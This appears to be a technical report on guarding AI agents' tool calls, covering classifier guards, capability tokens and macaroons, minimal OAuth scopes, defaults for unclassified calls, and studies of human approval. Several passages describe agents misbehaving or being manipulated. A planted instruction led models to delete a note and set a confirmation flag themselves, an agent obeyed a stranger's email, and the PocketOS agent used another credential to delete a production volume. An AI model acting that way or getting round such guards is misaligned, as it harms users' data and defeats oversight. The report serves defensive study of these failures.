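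All 23 models in this comparison detected more hazards with the longer rules than with the short ones, and 21 raised fewer false alarms. A smaller set of new scenarios gave similar results. The author works for a company that sells such a guard. AI models wrote and labelled the calls, and the labels followed the boundaries in the longer rules, so some apparent errors with the short rules may have been reasonable readings of an unclear sentence.

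### Combining fixed rules with a model

Fixed rules can handle familiar commands while a model judges the rest. *AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026) tested this combination with 170 text-matching rules and the language model DeepSeek-V3. If the rules block a call, it stays blocked. Otherwise the model also judges the call, and the guard follows the more severe verdict.

| Guard | Misses, 129 dangerous actions | False alarms, 133 safe actions | Typical time |
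|---|---|---|---|
| 50 simple patterns | 114 (88.4%) | 0 (0%) | 0.05 ms |
| AgentTrust's rules | 7 (5.4%) | 3 (2.3%) | 1.7 ms |
| Model alone | 3 (2.3%) | 10 (7.5%) | 1.3 s |
| AgentTrust's rules and model | 1 (0.8%) | 12 (9.0%) | 1.5 s |

A false alarm here includes a warning that doesn't stop the call, so the rate is not directly comparable with the false-block rates above. Because the guard always follows the more severe verdict, adding the model can reduce misses but can't remove false alarms. The model often flagged routine commands in a slightly unusual form, such as copying files to a staging server. It had no information about which servers or environments the project treated as safe.

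The rules did well partly because their author had developed them using this test. On a separate set of 630 actions, the rules missed 6.4% of the dangerous ones and the combination missed 0.3%, but the author had also added rules after finding gaps on that set. The results for the 50 simple patterns better indicate what happens when an agent does something the rules' author didn't expect. The patterns missed 114 dangerous actions, while the model, with only a short prompt, missed three.

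For unfamiliar services, AgentTrust's default matters more than its average accuracy. If no rule matches and the analyser finds no known danger sign, the rules allow the call. A private service's `settle` operation would probably match nothing, so the model would be the only remaining check. An experimental version runs the model only when a rule has already flagged the call as doubtful. This version causes fewer false alarms, but it would allow the `settle` call without running the model.

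### Coverage and auditing

The results support using a classifier for calls that no rule covers, especially when they would otherwise run unchecked. But a classifier is much harder to audit than an allowlist, because you can only find out which calls it permits by trying them, and it may judge the same call differently the next time. When Yang and colleagues had Claude Code's checker judge the same 24 out-of-scope calls three times under the original requests, it missed 13, 10 and 16.

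A provider can also change a hosted model without the guard's author noticing. In the decision model study, two models' detection rates changed by 2.5 to 3.8 percentage points when identical requests were sent two weeks apart. A model's written explanation helps a reviewer spot a misunderstanding, but it is weak evidence of the model's reasons, as was the PocketOS agent's explanation.

Errors may also cluster. Karunanithi considered a company with 200 tools, 60 of which read sensitive data, and an 8% chance of a wrong permission for each of the 60. If the errors were independent, the chance of at least one would be 1 − 0.92^60, or about 99%. But models that got one permission wrong tended to get others wrong too. Accounting for this lowered the estimated chance of any error to about 35%, but when errors occurred, they affected about 14 tools on average instead of five.

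If one classifier handles every call and misclassifies one operation of a private service, it may misclassify similar operations in the same way, and checking again with the same model could repeat the mistake. A reviewer who finds one error should therefore check related calls before trusting the classifier's other decisions about that service. Until then, the classifier's approval is weak evidence that an irreversible call is safe.

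## Limiting a call with capability tokens

A guard can prevent harm from a call it misjudges by giving the agent a capability token, a credential that allows only what the task needs. The service refuses anything else, so the guard doesn't have to predict everything a call will do. If the only token within the PocketOS agent's reach had been one for the staging environment, Railway would have refused to delete the production volume, even if the agent, the guard and a developer had all mistaken it for a staging volume.

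### Authority, attenuation and the confused deputy

A credential's authority is the set of operations it lets its holder perform. Many services divide authority into scopes, named permissions that each cover a group of operations. Xu (2026), in *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization*, defines the authority of a set of scopes *F* as everything that any scope in the set allows:

```
A(F) = union of M(s) for every scope s in F
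```

*M*(*s*) is the list of operations that the supplier publishes for scope *s*.

Attenuation means making a weaker token from a stronger one. For example, someone whose token gives access to all their private images could make a token that only allows reading one of them, and send that token to a friend.

A confused deputy is a program that has authority and is tricked into using it for someone who doesn't. In the classic example, a compiler has permission to write to a billing file that its users can't change. A user names that file as the output file, and the compiler overwrites the bills. An agent can make the same mistake when it reads a stranger's email and follows an instruction in it using its owner's credential. According to *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026), common agent frameworks still treat making a tool available as authorising its use. A narrow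 token limits what the stranger can do through the agent, but it doesn't stop the agent from following the stranger's instructions.

### OAuth scopes and more detailed requests

OAuth is the usual way to let one application use another service without giving it the user's password. The user signs in to the service and approves a list of scopes, and the application receives an access token for those scopes. *Beyond OAuth* (2026) points out that a scope permits an operation but doesn't limit its arguments to those the task needs. For example, a scope for sending payments would normally allow any amount to any recipient.

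Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell, in *OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests* (RFC 9396), add a field for such details. With invented values, a request to pay one month's rent might look like this:

```
{"type": "payment_initiation",
 "actions": ["initiate"],
 "instructedAmount": {"currency": "EUR", "amount": "900.00"},
 "creditorName": "Riverside Lettings"}
```

The authorization server, which issues the tokens, asks the user to approve this payment. It must reject a request that contains an unknown type or field, so a misspelt restriction causes an error instead of being ignored.

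An application can still easily ask for more access than it needs. If one object in a request lists the actions "read" and "write" and the data types "contacts" and "photos", it covers all four combinations. An application that only needs to read contacts and write to photos has to send two separate objects, or it will also get permission to write to contacts.

Each service defines its own types, and RFC 9396 provides no standard way to tell which of two requests is for more access. It also gives applications no way to look up the types a service accepts. *OAuth 2.0 RAR Metadata and Error Signaling* (Zehavi, 2026) proposes one, but until services adopt something like it, whoever writes a guard has to read each service's documentation.

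An application can also exchange broad permission for a narrower, short-lived token. In another example from Lodderstedt and colleagues, a user has approved account access and a payment, and the application asks for a token that can only list accounts. *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents* (2026) explains that related standards can restrict a token to one server or record that one party is acting for another.

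A short lifetime mostly helps against forgotten tokens. Railway's OAuth access tokens expire after an hour, so one left in an old file would soon be useless. But a deletion that takes nine seconds can easily finish before the token expires. According to Railway, tokens an application already holds can also keep working until they expire, even after a user withdraws the application's access.

### How a macaroon works

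With OAuth, an application has to ask the authorization server for each weaker token. *Macaroons* (Birgisson, Politz and colleagues, 2014) describes a token that any holder can weaken without contacting anyone. The token relies on HMAC, a function that computes a short code from a secret key and a text. The code doesn't reveal the key.

The service creates a macaroon by choosing an identifier and signing it with a secret key *K*. Each restriction, which Birgisson and colleagues call a caveat, gets a signature that uses the previous signature as its key. Their example is a token for a storage service that keeps data in numbered chunks:

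```
s0 = HMAC(K,  identifier)
s1 = HMAC(s0, "chunk in 100..500")
s2 = HMAC(s1, "operation == read")
```

The finished macaroon contains the identifier, both restrictions as readable text, and only the last signature, `s2`. When a request arrives, the service uses the identifier to find *K*, recomputes the chain and compares the result with `s2`. It then checks that the request satisfies every restriction.

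A holder can add a restriction because they have `s2`, the key for the next step:

```
s3 = HMAC(s2, "chunk == 235")
```

They pass on the longer list with `s3` and leave out `s2`.

To remove "chunk == 235", the recipient would need `s2`, the signature for the shorter list, but has only `s3`. Computing `s2` from `s3` would mean recovering an HMAC key from its output, which HMAC is designed to prevent. Removing or editing an earlier restriction would likewise require an earlier signature. Adding a looser rule such as "chunk in 1..1000" gives no extra access, because a request has to satisfy every rule on the list. López-Alt (2013) formally studied the security of these constructions in *Cryptographic Security of Macaroon Authorization Credentials*.

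Restricting a token doesn't help if the agent can find the less restricted original. The guard therefore has to add the restrictions itself and keep the original where the agent can't read it.

A restriction can also require proof from a third party, such as a service that checks requests for abuse. A company could enforce approvals by making the token work only with a fresh proof from its approval system, so an agent that skipped the guard's question could not make the call.

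Macaroons have some practical drawbacks. Only the issuing service can verify one, because verification requires *K*. The service also has to understand every restriction, because under Birgisson and colleagues' procedure it refuses a request if there is any restriction it can't confirm. This is safe, but it means a holder can't usefully invent new kinds of restriction. Madden (2024) lists the lack of a standard as a reason not to use macaroons.

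| Method | What it can limit | Who can make a weaker token | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|---|
| OAuth scopes | Groups of operations | The authorization server | Usually no limits on arguments |
| Rich Authorization Requests | Operations, targets and amounts | The authorization server | Different types for every service |
| Short-lived exchanged tokens | Whatever the server supports, for a limited time | The authorization server | Harm may take only seconds |
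| Macaroons | Anything the service can check | Any holder | No common standard |

### A token for adding one domain

PocketOS had created its token to manage custom domains. Suppose an agent has a similar but smaller task, connecting `api.shop.example` to the test version of a company's website. Railway's operation for this, `customDomainCreate`, takes a domain and the identifiers of a project, an environment and a service, according to a support thread started by andremaytorena (2026).

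Railway doesn't list macaroons among its token types, so the following token is imaginary:

```
s0 = HMAC(K,  "shop-key-7")
s1 = HMAC(s0, "operation == customDomainCreate")
s2 = HMAC(s1, "environment == staging")
s3 = HMAC(s2, "service == web")
s4 = HMAC(s3, "domain == api.shop.example")
s5 = HMAC(s4, "time < 2026-12-05 15:00 UTC")
```

The agent receives the identifier, the five restrictions and `s5`. The table shows how the service would respond to six calls if the guard let them all through.

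| Call | What the guard believed | What the service does |
|---|---|---|
| Add `api.shop.example` to `web` in staging at 14:30 | It does what the user asked | Accepts it |
| `volumeDelete` on `3d2c42fb-...` | It removes an old test volume | Refuses: wrong operation |
| Add `api.shop.example` to `web` in production | The environment is staging | Refuses: wrong environment |
| Add `login.shop.example` to `web` in staging | It is part of the task | Refuses: wrong domain |
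| Delete `api.shop.example` | It cleans up a mistake | Refuses: wrong operation |
| Repeat the accepted call at 15:10 | It is a harmless retry | Refuses: too late |

The service can apply the environment rule more reliably than the guard could, because it has records of which environment each resource belongs to. It must check every operation in a request, since one GraphQL mutation could both add a domain and delete a volume.

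The refused deletion also shows a drawback of narrow tokens. With this token, the agent can't undo its own change. The owner could let the agent delete this one domain, but it might then do so after customers had started using the domain.

According to Railway, a denied request to its API returns HTTP status 200, the usual code for success, with the error in the body. A guard that records only status codes would log a refused deletion as successful.

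### What Railway's tokens can limit

Railway's real tokens are much coarser than the imaginary one:

| Credential | What it reaches | Limit on operations |
|---|---|---|
| Account token | Everything the user can access | None beyond the user's own |
| Workspace token | One workspace | None listed |
| Project token | One environment in one project | None listed |
| OAuth token | Workspaces or projects that the user selects | Viewer, member or admin level |

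None of these is only for domains. Railway's *Scopes & User Consent* lists no domain-only scope, and asks developers who need a missing scope to get in touch. PocketOS could have limited its token to one environment, but apparently not to domains. Abdelwahab was therefore only partly right to write, after the PocketOS deletion, that the right scope had existed but the process of creating a token hadn't made the choice obvious.

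The closest fit is an OAuth token at member level, which gives an application the same access as a person with that role. Railway's *Feedback* page on roles explains that workspace members can't delete services, volumes or projects, so such a token should have blocked the PocketOS deletion even in production. The equivalent level for a single project, editor, gives access to less, but Railway's *Project Members* mentions only services and projects, not volumes, as examples of what an editor can't delete. An owner who wants to rely on an editor-level token should first test whether it can delete a spare volume.

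Even a member-level token allows far more than adding a domain. Workspace members can also create projects and change variables, the settings that a running program reads. An agent with such a token couldn't delete the production database, but it could disconnect the website from it by changing the variable that holds the database's address.

Railway advises agents to choose the narrowest token that will do the job. In the same guide, it recommends its command-line program to agents working in a user's terminal. But that program requests admin access to workspaces and projects at every login, according to the source code Railway published for version 5.6.1. The user's own role still limits this access, but the role of an owner or administrator doesn't restrict it at all.

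If Railway added a scope called "domains", the name might not reveal whether it covered connecting a domain the customer already owns, buying a new one, or both. Railway sells domains, charges the customer's existing payment method and renews the domains automatically by default.

### Finding the smallest sufficient permission

To choose a scope, the guard has to know which operations the task needs and which scopes allow them. Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025), in *MiniScope*, automate the choice for services that document this. The agent first submits a plan of its calls. MiniScope looks up the scopes that allow each call, then solves this problem:

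```
minimise   sum of cost(v) × x(v) over all scopes v
so that    at least one chosen scope allows each planned call
```

The variable *x*(*v*) is 1 if MiniScope chooses scope *v* and 0 otherwise. Each scope's weight is the number of API methods it allows. MiniScope then asks the user to approve any chosen scopes the agent doesn't already have. The user can approve them for one operation, for the session or permanently.

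Choosing a scope isn't trivial, because 24 of Google Calendar's 37 methods work with scopes from more than one branch of its permission hierarchy. Scope names can also mislead, because Outlook's `Mail.Read` isn't a smaller version of `Mail.ReadWrite`, as its name suggests.

Zhu and colleagues tested MiniScope on invented requests for ten real applications, including Gmail, Slack and Zoom. MiniScope added 1–6% to the agent's running time. When they gave the same information to language models, three commercial models found the smallest permission for 70–83% of requests, and two open models for 20–34%. On tasks that used several applications, the commercial models' choices allowed 1.12 to 1.49 times as many methods as MiniScope's did. These models are now old, but a newer paper, *Trust Is Not a Score* (2026), cites a study in which leading models left out permissions that a task needed and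 granted sensitive ones that it didn't.

Counting methods settles which permission is smallest, but not necessarily which is safest. Xu gives the example of reading the metadata of a project in BigQuery. Either of two Google scopes is enough:

| Scope | Methods allowed | Services reached | Methods that change data |
|---|---|---|---|
| `bigquery` | 286 | 10 | 144 |
| `cloud-platform.read-only` | 565 | 27 | 61 |

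By MiniScope's measure, `bigquery` is the smaller permission, so an agent that only needs to read would receive 144 ways to change something. The alternative lets it read from many more services. Which is safer depends on whether the owner worries more about damage or disclosure. The figure of 61 for a "read-only" scope also needs checking, because Xu identified changes mainly by HTTP method, which can misclassify a read as a write.

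Xu measured how often this happens by generating tasks from the way Google and Microsoft group their operations. About 30% of tasks in Microsoft Graph, the API for Microsoft 365, and 3.2% of Google tasks had at least two sufficient permissions, neither of which contained the other. Real agents may have a different mix of tasks. Microsoft also gives each permission a privilege level from 1 to 4, but this doesn't always help in choosing between permissions. For one task, a permission that reaches 355 addresses has the same level as one that reaches 11.

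Six leading models then chose between sufficient permissions for the Microsoft tasks. In 99.0% of 1,708 decisions, they avoided permissions that contained a smaller sufficient one. But in 22.1%, another option was at least as good on all four of Xu's risk measures (the number of operations, the number of changes, the services reached and access to administrative functions) and better on at least one. Xu recommends showing the alternatives to whoever approves the permission.

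For many unfamiliar services, the guard lacks the information it needs to compute a token's limits. Xu examined OpenAPI descriptions of 1,263 APIs and found that their security fields mostly record how a client logs in, not which operations a credential allows.

Another approach is to derive the permission from the user's request. The system in *Beyond OAuth* derives permissions that cover both operations and their arguments. In its tests, which included AgentDojo, it allowed every harmless task and blocked every malicious call. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* warns that a request can be ambiguous and that a manipulated prompt may lead to a broader permission than the user intended. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) reduces the risk from manipulated prompts by fixing a limit for the whole task before the agent reads any files or tool results. If the agent passes work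 to other agents, it can give them authority only within that limit.

### Permissions in published integrations

Companies often request more than their products need, even when a narrower scope exists. Zhu and colleagues examined nine connectors, which link ChatGPT or Claude to outside services, and found excessive permissions in six:

| Connector | Methods allowed | Methods allowed by the smallest sufficient scopes |
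|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT: Gmail | 50 | 32 |
| ChatGPT: Google Calendar | 12 | 5 |
| ChatGPT: Notion | 32 | 13 |
| ChatGPT: Dropbox | 44 | 25 |
| Claude: Google Drive | 45 | 27 |
| Claude: Notion | 32 | 29 |

As of December 2025, ChatGPT's connectors for Gmail and Google Calendar offered only read functions, but their permissions also covered changing and deleting emails and events. The companies may have corrected this since. The extra permissions were avoidable because the services already offered narrower scopes.

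The problem predates agents. *Improving Google A2A Protocol* (2025) cites research by Dimova and colleagues, who found unnecessary scopes in 18.5% of OAuth deployments on the web.

Buyers often can't check the permissions in advance. Longo, Verna and colleagues (*Lost in Permissions*, 2026) collected data on more than 8,000 applications for Microsoft 365 and could obtain both a description and a list of permissions for only 1,069. When they installed the Wikipedia application in three ways, only one showed any information about permissions. Many applications requested access to a whole organisation's data. `User.Read.All`, for example, covers everyone's profile, while `User.Read` covers only that of the person who signed in. Some applications lacked permissions they needed for their stated purpose.

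### When a broker holds the credential

If a service offers only broad tokens, the guard's owner can put a broker in front of it. The broker keeps the real credential, checks each call from the agent and adds the credential only to calls it accepts. MiniScope works this way and gives the agent a session token that the outside services wouldn't recognise.

Leaving the powerful credential with the broker at least keeps it out of the agent's files. Noyan argues in *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* that an agent can't misuse a credential it doesn't have, however cleverly it reasons. But the agent can still misuse the credential indirectly by persuading the broker to accept a harmful call, which makes the broker a confused deputy.

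To avoid that, the broker has to determine what each call does, which capability tokens were supposed to make unnecessary. A broker for Railway would have to parse the GraphQL body and find out which environment a volume belongs to. MiniScope needs a table that matches each MCP tool with the API methods behind it, and Zhu and colleagues assume that a service's methods do what the documentation promises. If the broker's interpretation is wrong, the service receives a valid, powerful credential and executes the call.

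A broker is much easier to trust if it accepts only a few operations that someone has studied. For the domain task, it could accept `customDomainCreate` with fixed arguments and refuse everything else. This is still an allowlist, but the broker enforces it, so the agent can't get around it unless it finds another credential, as the PocketOS agent did.

### Harm within the permitted scope

A token can't prevent harm from the operations it allows. In the domain example, the staging website might contain copies of real customer records and have no login page. Giving it a public address could then expose those records, even though the call would satisfy all five restrictions. Zhu and colleagues acknowledge the same limit in MiniScope, which doesn't stop an attacker from getting the agent to use an approved tool with different arguments.

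Tokens can also be harmful in combination, like the parts of the lethal trifecta. With one narrow token for reading mail and another for posting messages, an agent could post the contents of a private email. Neither service could detect this, because each receives only its own calls.

The guard therefore still has to judge the calls a token allows, but it has fewer kinds to judge. With the imaginary domain token, the owner would need to study one operation on one service and could leave the rest of Railway's API unclassified.

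## Handling calls that stay unclassified

If a service offers only broad tokens, an agent can still make calls that nobody has studied. One is the earlier example, `POST /v2/ledger/settle`, sent to a company's private finance service. No allowlist entry matches it, the service declares nothing and offers no dry run, and the classifier can only guess. The guard still has to decide how to handle the call.

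### Five possible defaults

| Default | What happens to the `settle` call | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Allow | It runs | If it pays an invoice, the company may first learn of it from the bank statement |
| Ask | It waits for a person's answer | The person may know no more than the guard |
| Refuse | It never reaches the service | The agent may fail at a harmless task |
| Delay | It waits until the task ends or someone has looked into it | The agent may need the result to continue |
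| Run only if the earlier state has been saved | It runs once a copy of the ledger exists | A copy of the ledger doesn't bring back a payment |

In 1975, the computer scientists Saltzer and Schroeder described fail-safe defaults, the principle that a system should refuse access unless it has a reason to permit it. They argued that the owner soon hears about an error in a rule that grants access, because it usually refuses someone who then complains, while an error in a rule that excludes people lets someone in and may go unnoticed.

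The principle rules out "allow" for an unknown call. But users may switch off a guard that refuses too much. One user of the coding agent Cursor turned off its delete protection so that the agent could clear out duplicate files, and the agent later deleted 90% of the project. The case is one of 290 public reports of file damage and leaks by coding agents collected in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026).

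A default also helps only when the guard recognises a call as unknown. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) used a language model to sort tools by consequence, such as spending or deleting, and simulated a rule that blocked each category. The rules missed 14% of the tools they should have blocked. Sending the model's low-confidence answers to a person reduced this to 11%, but raised the share of tools blocked needlessly from 4% to 7%. Only three of the 120 tools fell below the confidence threshold, so most of the mistakes were above it. A guard should therefore treat a call as unknown when evidence is missing, such as when nobody has tested the operation, even if the classifier is confident.

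### Saving the earlier state first

Zhong and colleagues built YoloFS, a file system that keeps an agent's changes in a separate staging area until the user accepts them. It also takes a snapshot after each command, so the agent can see which files the command changed and return to an earlier snapshot. In 11 tasks with hidden destructive side effects, agents noticed and undid the damage in eight. In the other three, the changes looked consistent with the task, but they stayed in the staging area, where the user could still reject them. On 112 routine tasks, agents succeeded as often as they did without YoloFS (99%) and interrupted the user less.

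This is a good default for an unfamiliar program that works on local files, because nobody has to predict what the program will do. It doesn't help when an agent reads a secret, because the read can't be undone, so YoloFS asks the user before an agent opens a sensitive file.

Saving local state helps much less with calls to outside services. *ACRFence* (2026) points out that restoring a checkpoint can't undo what an agent has already done elsewhere, and can make matters worse. Suppose an agent transfers money, and its software then restores a checkpoint from before the transfer. The agent tries again with a new reference number, so the bank accepts a second payment. Waghmare and Sufi therefore don't let a saved file justify a lower risk class for payments, access changes or anything the call triggers automatically.

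### Holding the call back

*Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that makes local changes in a shadow copy and holds messages and other external actions in an outbox until the task is ready to finish. The system then checks how information moved between the steps and either releases or discards the waiting actions. In one example, an agent investigating an outage reads logs that contain a secret key, summarises them and prepares a message to colleagues. Each step is routine, but the message may contain something derived from the key.

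Cordon stopped the harmful effects in all 45 risky workflows its designers tested, while imitations of existing defences stopped them in 14. The designers also report shorter task times, but these exclude time spent waiting for approval, which could be the largest drawback of a delay.

Holding back the `settle` call would give someone time to find out what it does. But if the agent needs the response for its next step, the task stops there. *Cordon* also warns that an external action can't be rolled back once the system releases it, so the check before release has to be right.

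A delayed call needs a deadline and a safe outcome if nobody responds in time. *Right to History* (2026) describes a design in which an agent can continue with other actions while one waits for a person's decision. If the owner has set a time limit, the system treats a lack of response within that limit as a refusal.

### Why nobody asks

When a call stays unclassified, most guard developers would probably choose to ask a person, as the MCP specification recommends. The host can prompt the user before it forwards the call, or the server can ask through elicitation, a request for the user's input that the host relays if it supports the feature. In November 2026, *When Neither Side Confirms* measured how often either happens by default.

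The researchers sampled 1,000 code repositories from the official MCP registry, taking the 200 with the most GitHub stars and 800 at random. They counted a tool as destructive if a call to it could irreversibly delete or overwrite data, send messages, move money or run arbitrary commands. A program flagged tools that were likely to be destructive, and language models read the code of a sample of these and identified 269 as destructive. When the researchers checked 40 repositories in full, they found that the program had missed 83% of the destructive tools, so they included the missed tools in their estimate.

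An estimated 90% of destructive tools have no server-side confirmation (95% interval: 82% to 95%). About 70% have no safeguard, and 20% have only an annotation. Another 8.9% require a confirmation that the model can supply itself, for example by adding `confirm=true` to the call. Fewer than 1% require confirmation from a person.

Even servers that use elicitation often let a destructive action proceed without an answer. The researchers read every sampled repository that mentioned the feature and found 168 tools that use it by default before a destructive action. If the host can't relay the question, 100 of them accept a flag that the model can set, 30 run anyway and 38 refuse.

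The researchers traced what 41 popular open-source hosts do with an ordinary MCP call in a default setup. They found no approval step in 32 of them, including 16 of the 25 applications and all 16 software development kits (SDKs), which are libraries for building agents. Of the other nine, seven prompt the user, one decides from the tool's annotations and one uses a learned classifier. A larger study, *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* (Majeed, Mahmoud and Nadi, 2026), examined 1,723 applications and found code that waits for the user's approval in only 37.2% of them. A fifth had neither an approval step nor a way to restrict which tools were enabled.

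*When Neither Side Confirms* then paired each of the 269 destructive tools with each of the 25 applications. In 60.7% of the pairs, the call would run without enforced human approval. The host would prompt for approval in 31.9% and the server in only 2.9%, so whether a person must approve the call depends almost entirely on the host. Adding seven closed-source applications, including Claude Code and Cursor, lowers the unapproved share to 47.5%. These are shares of pairs, so a rarely used application counts as much as a popular one.

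Developers on each side have reasons to leave the confirmation prompt to the other. A server for the mapping program QGIS skips its own confirmation by default because, according to its documentation, "MCP clients gate destructive tool calls themselves". SDK developers leave approval to whoever builds an application with the SDK, and 12 of the 16 SDKs offer an approval option or a place to add one. A server can't tell whether the host has already prompted the user, so a server that prompts as a precaution may repeat the host's question. The specification also doesn't define whether a server should proceed or refuse when the host can't relay a question.

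One database server in the registry has a tool that deletes an entire database. The tool asks the user to confirm through elicitation, but deletes the database anyway if the host doesn't support elicitation. The coding agent Cline neither relays such questions nor prompts before MCP calls by default, so a Cline user would lose the database without being asked.

The researchers asked agents to delete one note and planted an instruction to delete another, titled "tax records 2025". Four of five low-cost models carried out the planted deletion in 479 of 960 runs, and the fifth never did. A confirmation flag gave little protection. Even when the planted text didn't mention `confirm=true`, 127 of 169 attempted deletions succeeded because the model set the flag itself.

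### What more prompts would achieve

The researchers calculated how three changes would affect the 25 applications:

| Change | Destructive pairs that run unapproved | Destructive pairs the server refuses | Harmless pairs in which the user is asked |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 60.7% | 0.7% | 32.5% |
| Every host relays elicitation | 56.7% | 0.0% | 35.2% |
| Every host prompts unless a tool is annotated read-only or non-destructive | 5.4% | 0.7% | 82.6% |
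| Every destructive tool refuses unless a person answers | 0.0% | 71.0% | 32.5% |

The last column covers tools that the program had flagged as possibly destructive but that turned out not to be.

Relaying elicitation requests to the user changes little because most destructive tools never send them. If every tool required an answer before running, no call would run unapproved, but most calls would fail because the host can't relay the question. Some would fail even though the user had just approved them in the host's own prompt. The researchers suggest letting a host declare that it obtains human approval, so that servers need to refuse calls only when nobody has asked the user for approval.

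Prompting by annotation handles all but 5.4% of tools. The remainder are destructive tools annotated as read-only or non-destructive. Some of those annotations may be accurate, since MCP doesn't class sending a message as destructive. Counting the tools that the program overlooked raises the remainder to at least 10.6% across all 41 hosts.

The new default produces many prompts. Suppose these shares also applied to calls, and an agent made 200 calls to flagged tools, ten of them destructive. The new default would reduce the unapproved destructive calls from about six to fewer than one. It would also raise the number of needless prompts from about 62 to 157, or 17 extra prompts for each additional destructive call that someone gets to review. Whether the extra prompts are worthwhile depends on how well people review.

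### What a person's approval is worth

In August 2026, Anthropic published an experiment with 1,053 paid professional testers. Each worked on coding tasks with Claude Code in an environment built for the study. During the session, the experiment replaced the text of a permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, though approving it did no damage. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on what.

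Only 143 of 1,053 testers (13.6%) blocked the command they were shown, while Claude Code's classifier blocked 937 of the same 1,053 commands (89%). People blocked about 17% of commands early in a session and about 5% once they had seen 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's rate stayed the same. People caught only six of the 116 commands that the classifier allowed, so asking a person to check its approvals would have added almost nothing in this setting.

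The testers were not working on their own projects and had nothing to lose, so people protecting their own data might do better. Anthropic also makes the classifier that performed best in the comparison. The planted commands were clearly dangerous, so the 89% doesn't show how the classifier would handle an obscure operation such as `settle`.

Anthropic examined real sessions that its safety systems had flagged, looking for serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested. It found such harm in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those with the classifier. Users chose their own mode, though, so the two groups may have been doing different work.

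Claude Code's users approve 97% of permission prompts. Most of those prompts probably concern routine commands, so the high rate doesn't prove that users are careless. When Claude presents a plan for approval, they reject 39% of plans. They may do so because they dislike the design rather than because they see a danger, but the figure suggests that they read and evaluate the plans.

People did better in two smaller experiments. In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026), 80 volunteers judged requests from a simulated agent. In Yan's experiment, people who don't work in the software industry supervised an agent through a simulated day of email, travel and purchases, in which some actions went beyond the task.

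| Experiment | Share of requests that were harmful or beyond the task | Share of those that people approved |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | One per session | 86% |
| Hossain and colleagues, ordinary prompt | 6 of 12 | 55% |
| Yan, asked about every action | 7 of 18 | 40% |

The experiments differ in too many ways to isolate a cause, but the rarity of harmful requests is a likely one. People keep looking if they find a problem in every second request, but after approving 50 harmless commands they expect the next one to be harmless too. An agent's real calls are much more like that run of harmless commands.

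In Yan's experiment, people who set standing rules in advance blocked fewer excessive actions overall than people who had no rules. The 35 people in the group with rules each set one for four kinds of action, and they chose "ask" for 114 of the 140 rules. They then approved 67% of the excessive actions they were asked about.

### What a prompt should show

According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), most approval prompts in current products show a raw command on a single line. Zhong and colleagues found that uninformative prompts contributed to 31 of their 290 reports. One such prompt showed only `python3 setup.py`, with no description of what the script would do.

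Hossain and colleagues measured the value of adding information. In one of their scenarios, a user allows an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. The agent copies the full invoice rows into `report.csv` and asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool and the recipient are both permitted, so an ordinary prompt gives no sign of a problem. Volunteers saw one of four kinds of prompt:

| Prompt | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median decision time |
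|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16 s |
| With the exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23 s |
| With the user's original instruction and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 39 s |
| The same facts, with the combined consequence stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33 s |

Each prompt had only 20 reviewers, and the benefit of the last step is uncertain. After adjustment, the difference could range from 20 percentage points fewer unsafe approvals to 4 points more. There is stronger evidence for showing the instruction, the arguments and the history.

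With an unknown call, the guard can't state the consequence. It shouldn't present a guess as a fact either, because the reviewer may rely on it. Hossain and colleagues recommend showing gaps in the evidence as gaps. For the `settle` call, with invented details, a prompt might look like this:

Suppose a user asks an agent to "Reconcile the March invoices. Don't pay anything." The agent proposes calling `POST /v2/ledger/settle` on Harrow Ltd invoice 2207, for 4,180 euros. The agent's credential can make payments, but the guard does not know whether "settle" records a payment or makes one, or whether anyone can reverse it. The guard shows the user the original request, the proposed call, and what is known and not known about it. It adds that the finance systems team may know the answers, and that if the user refuses, invoice 2207 stays open and the agent continues.

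[Refuse]  [Hold and ask finance]  [Allow this call once]
```

The first line matters most here, because a reviewer who reads it next to "Not known" has good reason to refuse even without knowing anything about the service. The guard should take the call's details from the request itself, not from the agent's description, and ask for approval again if the arguments change after approval.

The prompt has no "always allow" button. Anthropic reports that 62% of Claude Code users have used a mode that skips permission checks or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands. *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) warns against treating repeated approvals as a lasting preference. In its survey of software practitioners, 48% said they read permission requests carefully, 21% said they approved them by default and 34% said they had become less careful over time. The paper also recommends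 distinguishing between refusing one action and refusing a whole approach. Otherwise, an agent that can't call `settle` may look for another way to pay the invoice.

### When to refuse or delay instead

A rough calculation shows when refusing is better than asking. Let *p* be the chance that an unknown call is harmful, *H* the cost of the harm, *m* the share of harmful calls that a person approves, and *B* the cost of refusing a harmless call. The expected losses are

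```
asking:    p × m × H
refusing:  (1 − p) × B
```

Suppose one unknown call in 100 is harmful and a needless refusal costs 10 euros of someone's time. If people approve 86% of the harmful calls they are asked about, as in Anthropic's experiment, refusing is better than asking once the possible harm exceeds about 1,150 euros. If they approve 24%, as with the best prompt in the volunteer study, the threshold rises to about 4,100 euros. The calculation leaves out the time that questions take and the harmless calls that people refuse, so it somewhat overstates the case for asking.

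A guard should also refuse if nobody is there to answer. Codex does this, and in the deletion tests it refused calls that nobody could approve. For some kinds of call, approval in a prompt shouldn't be enough. Claude Code's classifier is designed never to approve sending code or secrets to an outside destination, so a user who wants to do this has to leave auto mode or run the command themselves.

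Blocked calls can keep an agent from finishing its task. Hossain and colleagues tested a guard that blocked every call it couldn't assess. One agent completed 83% of its legitimate tasks when the guard had a full record of earlier steps, and 77% when the record was incomplete. Claude Code limits the problem by returning to manual approval after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session.

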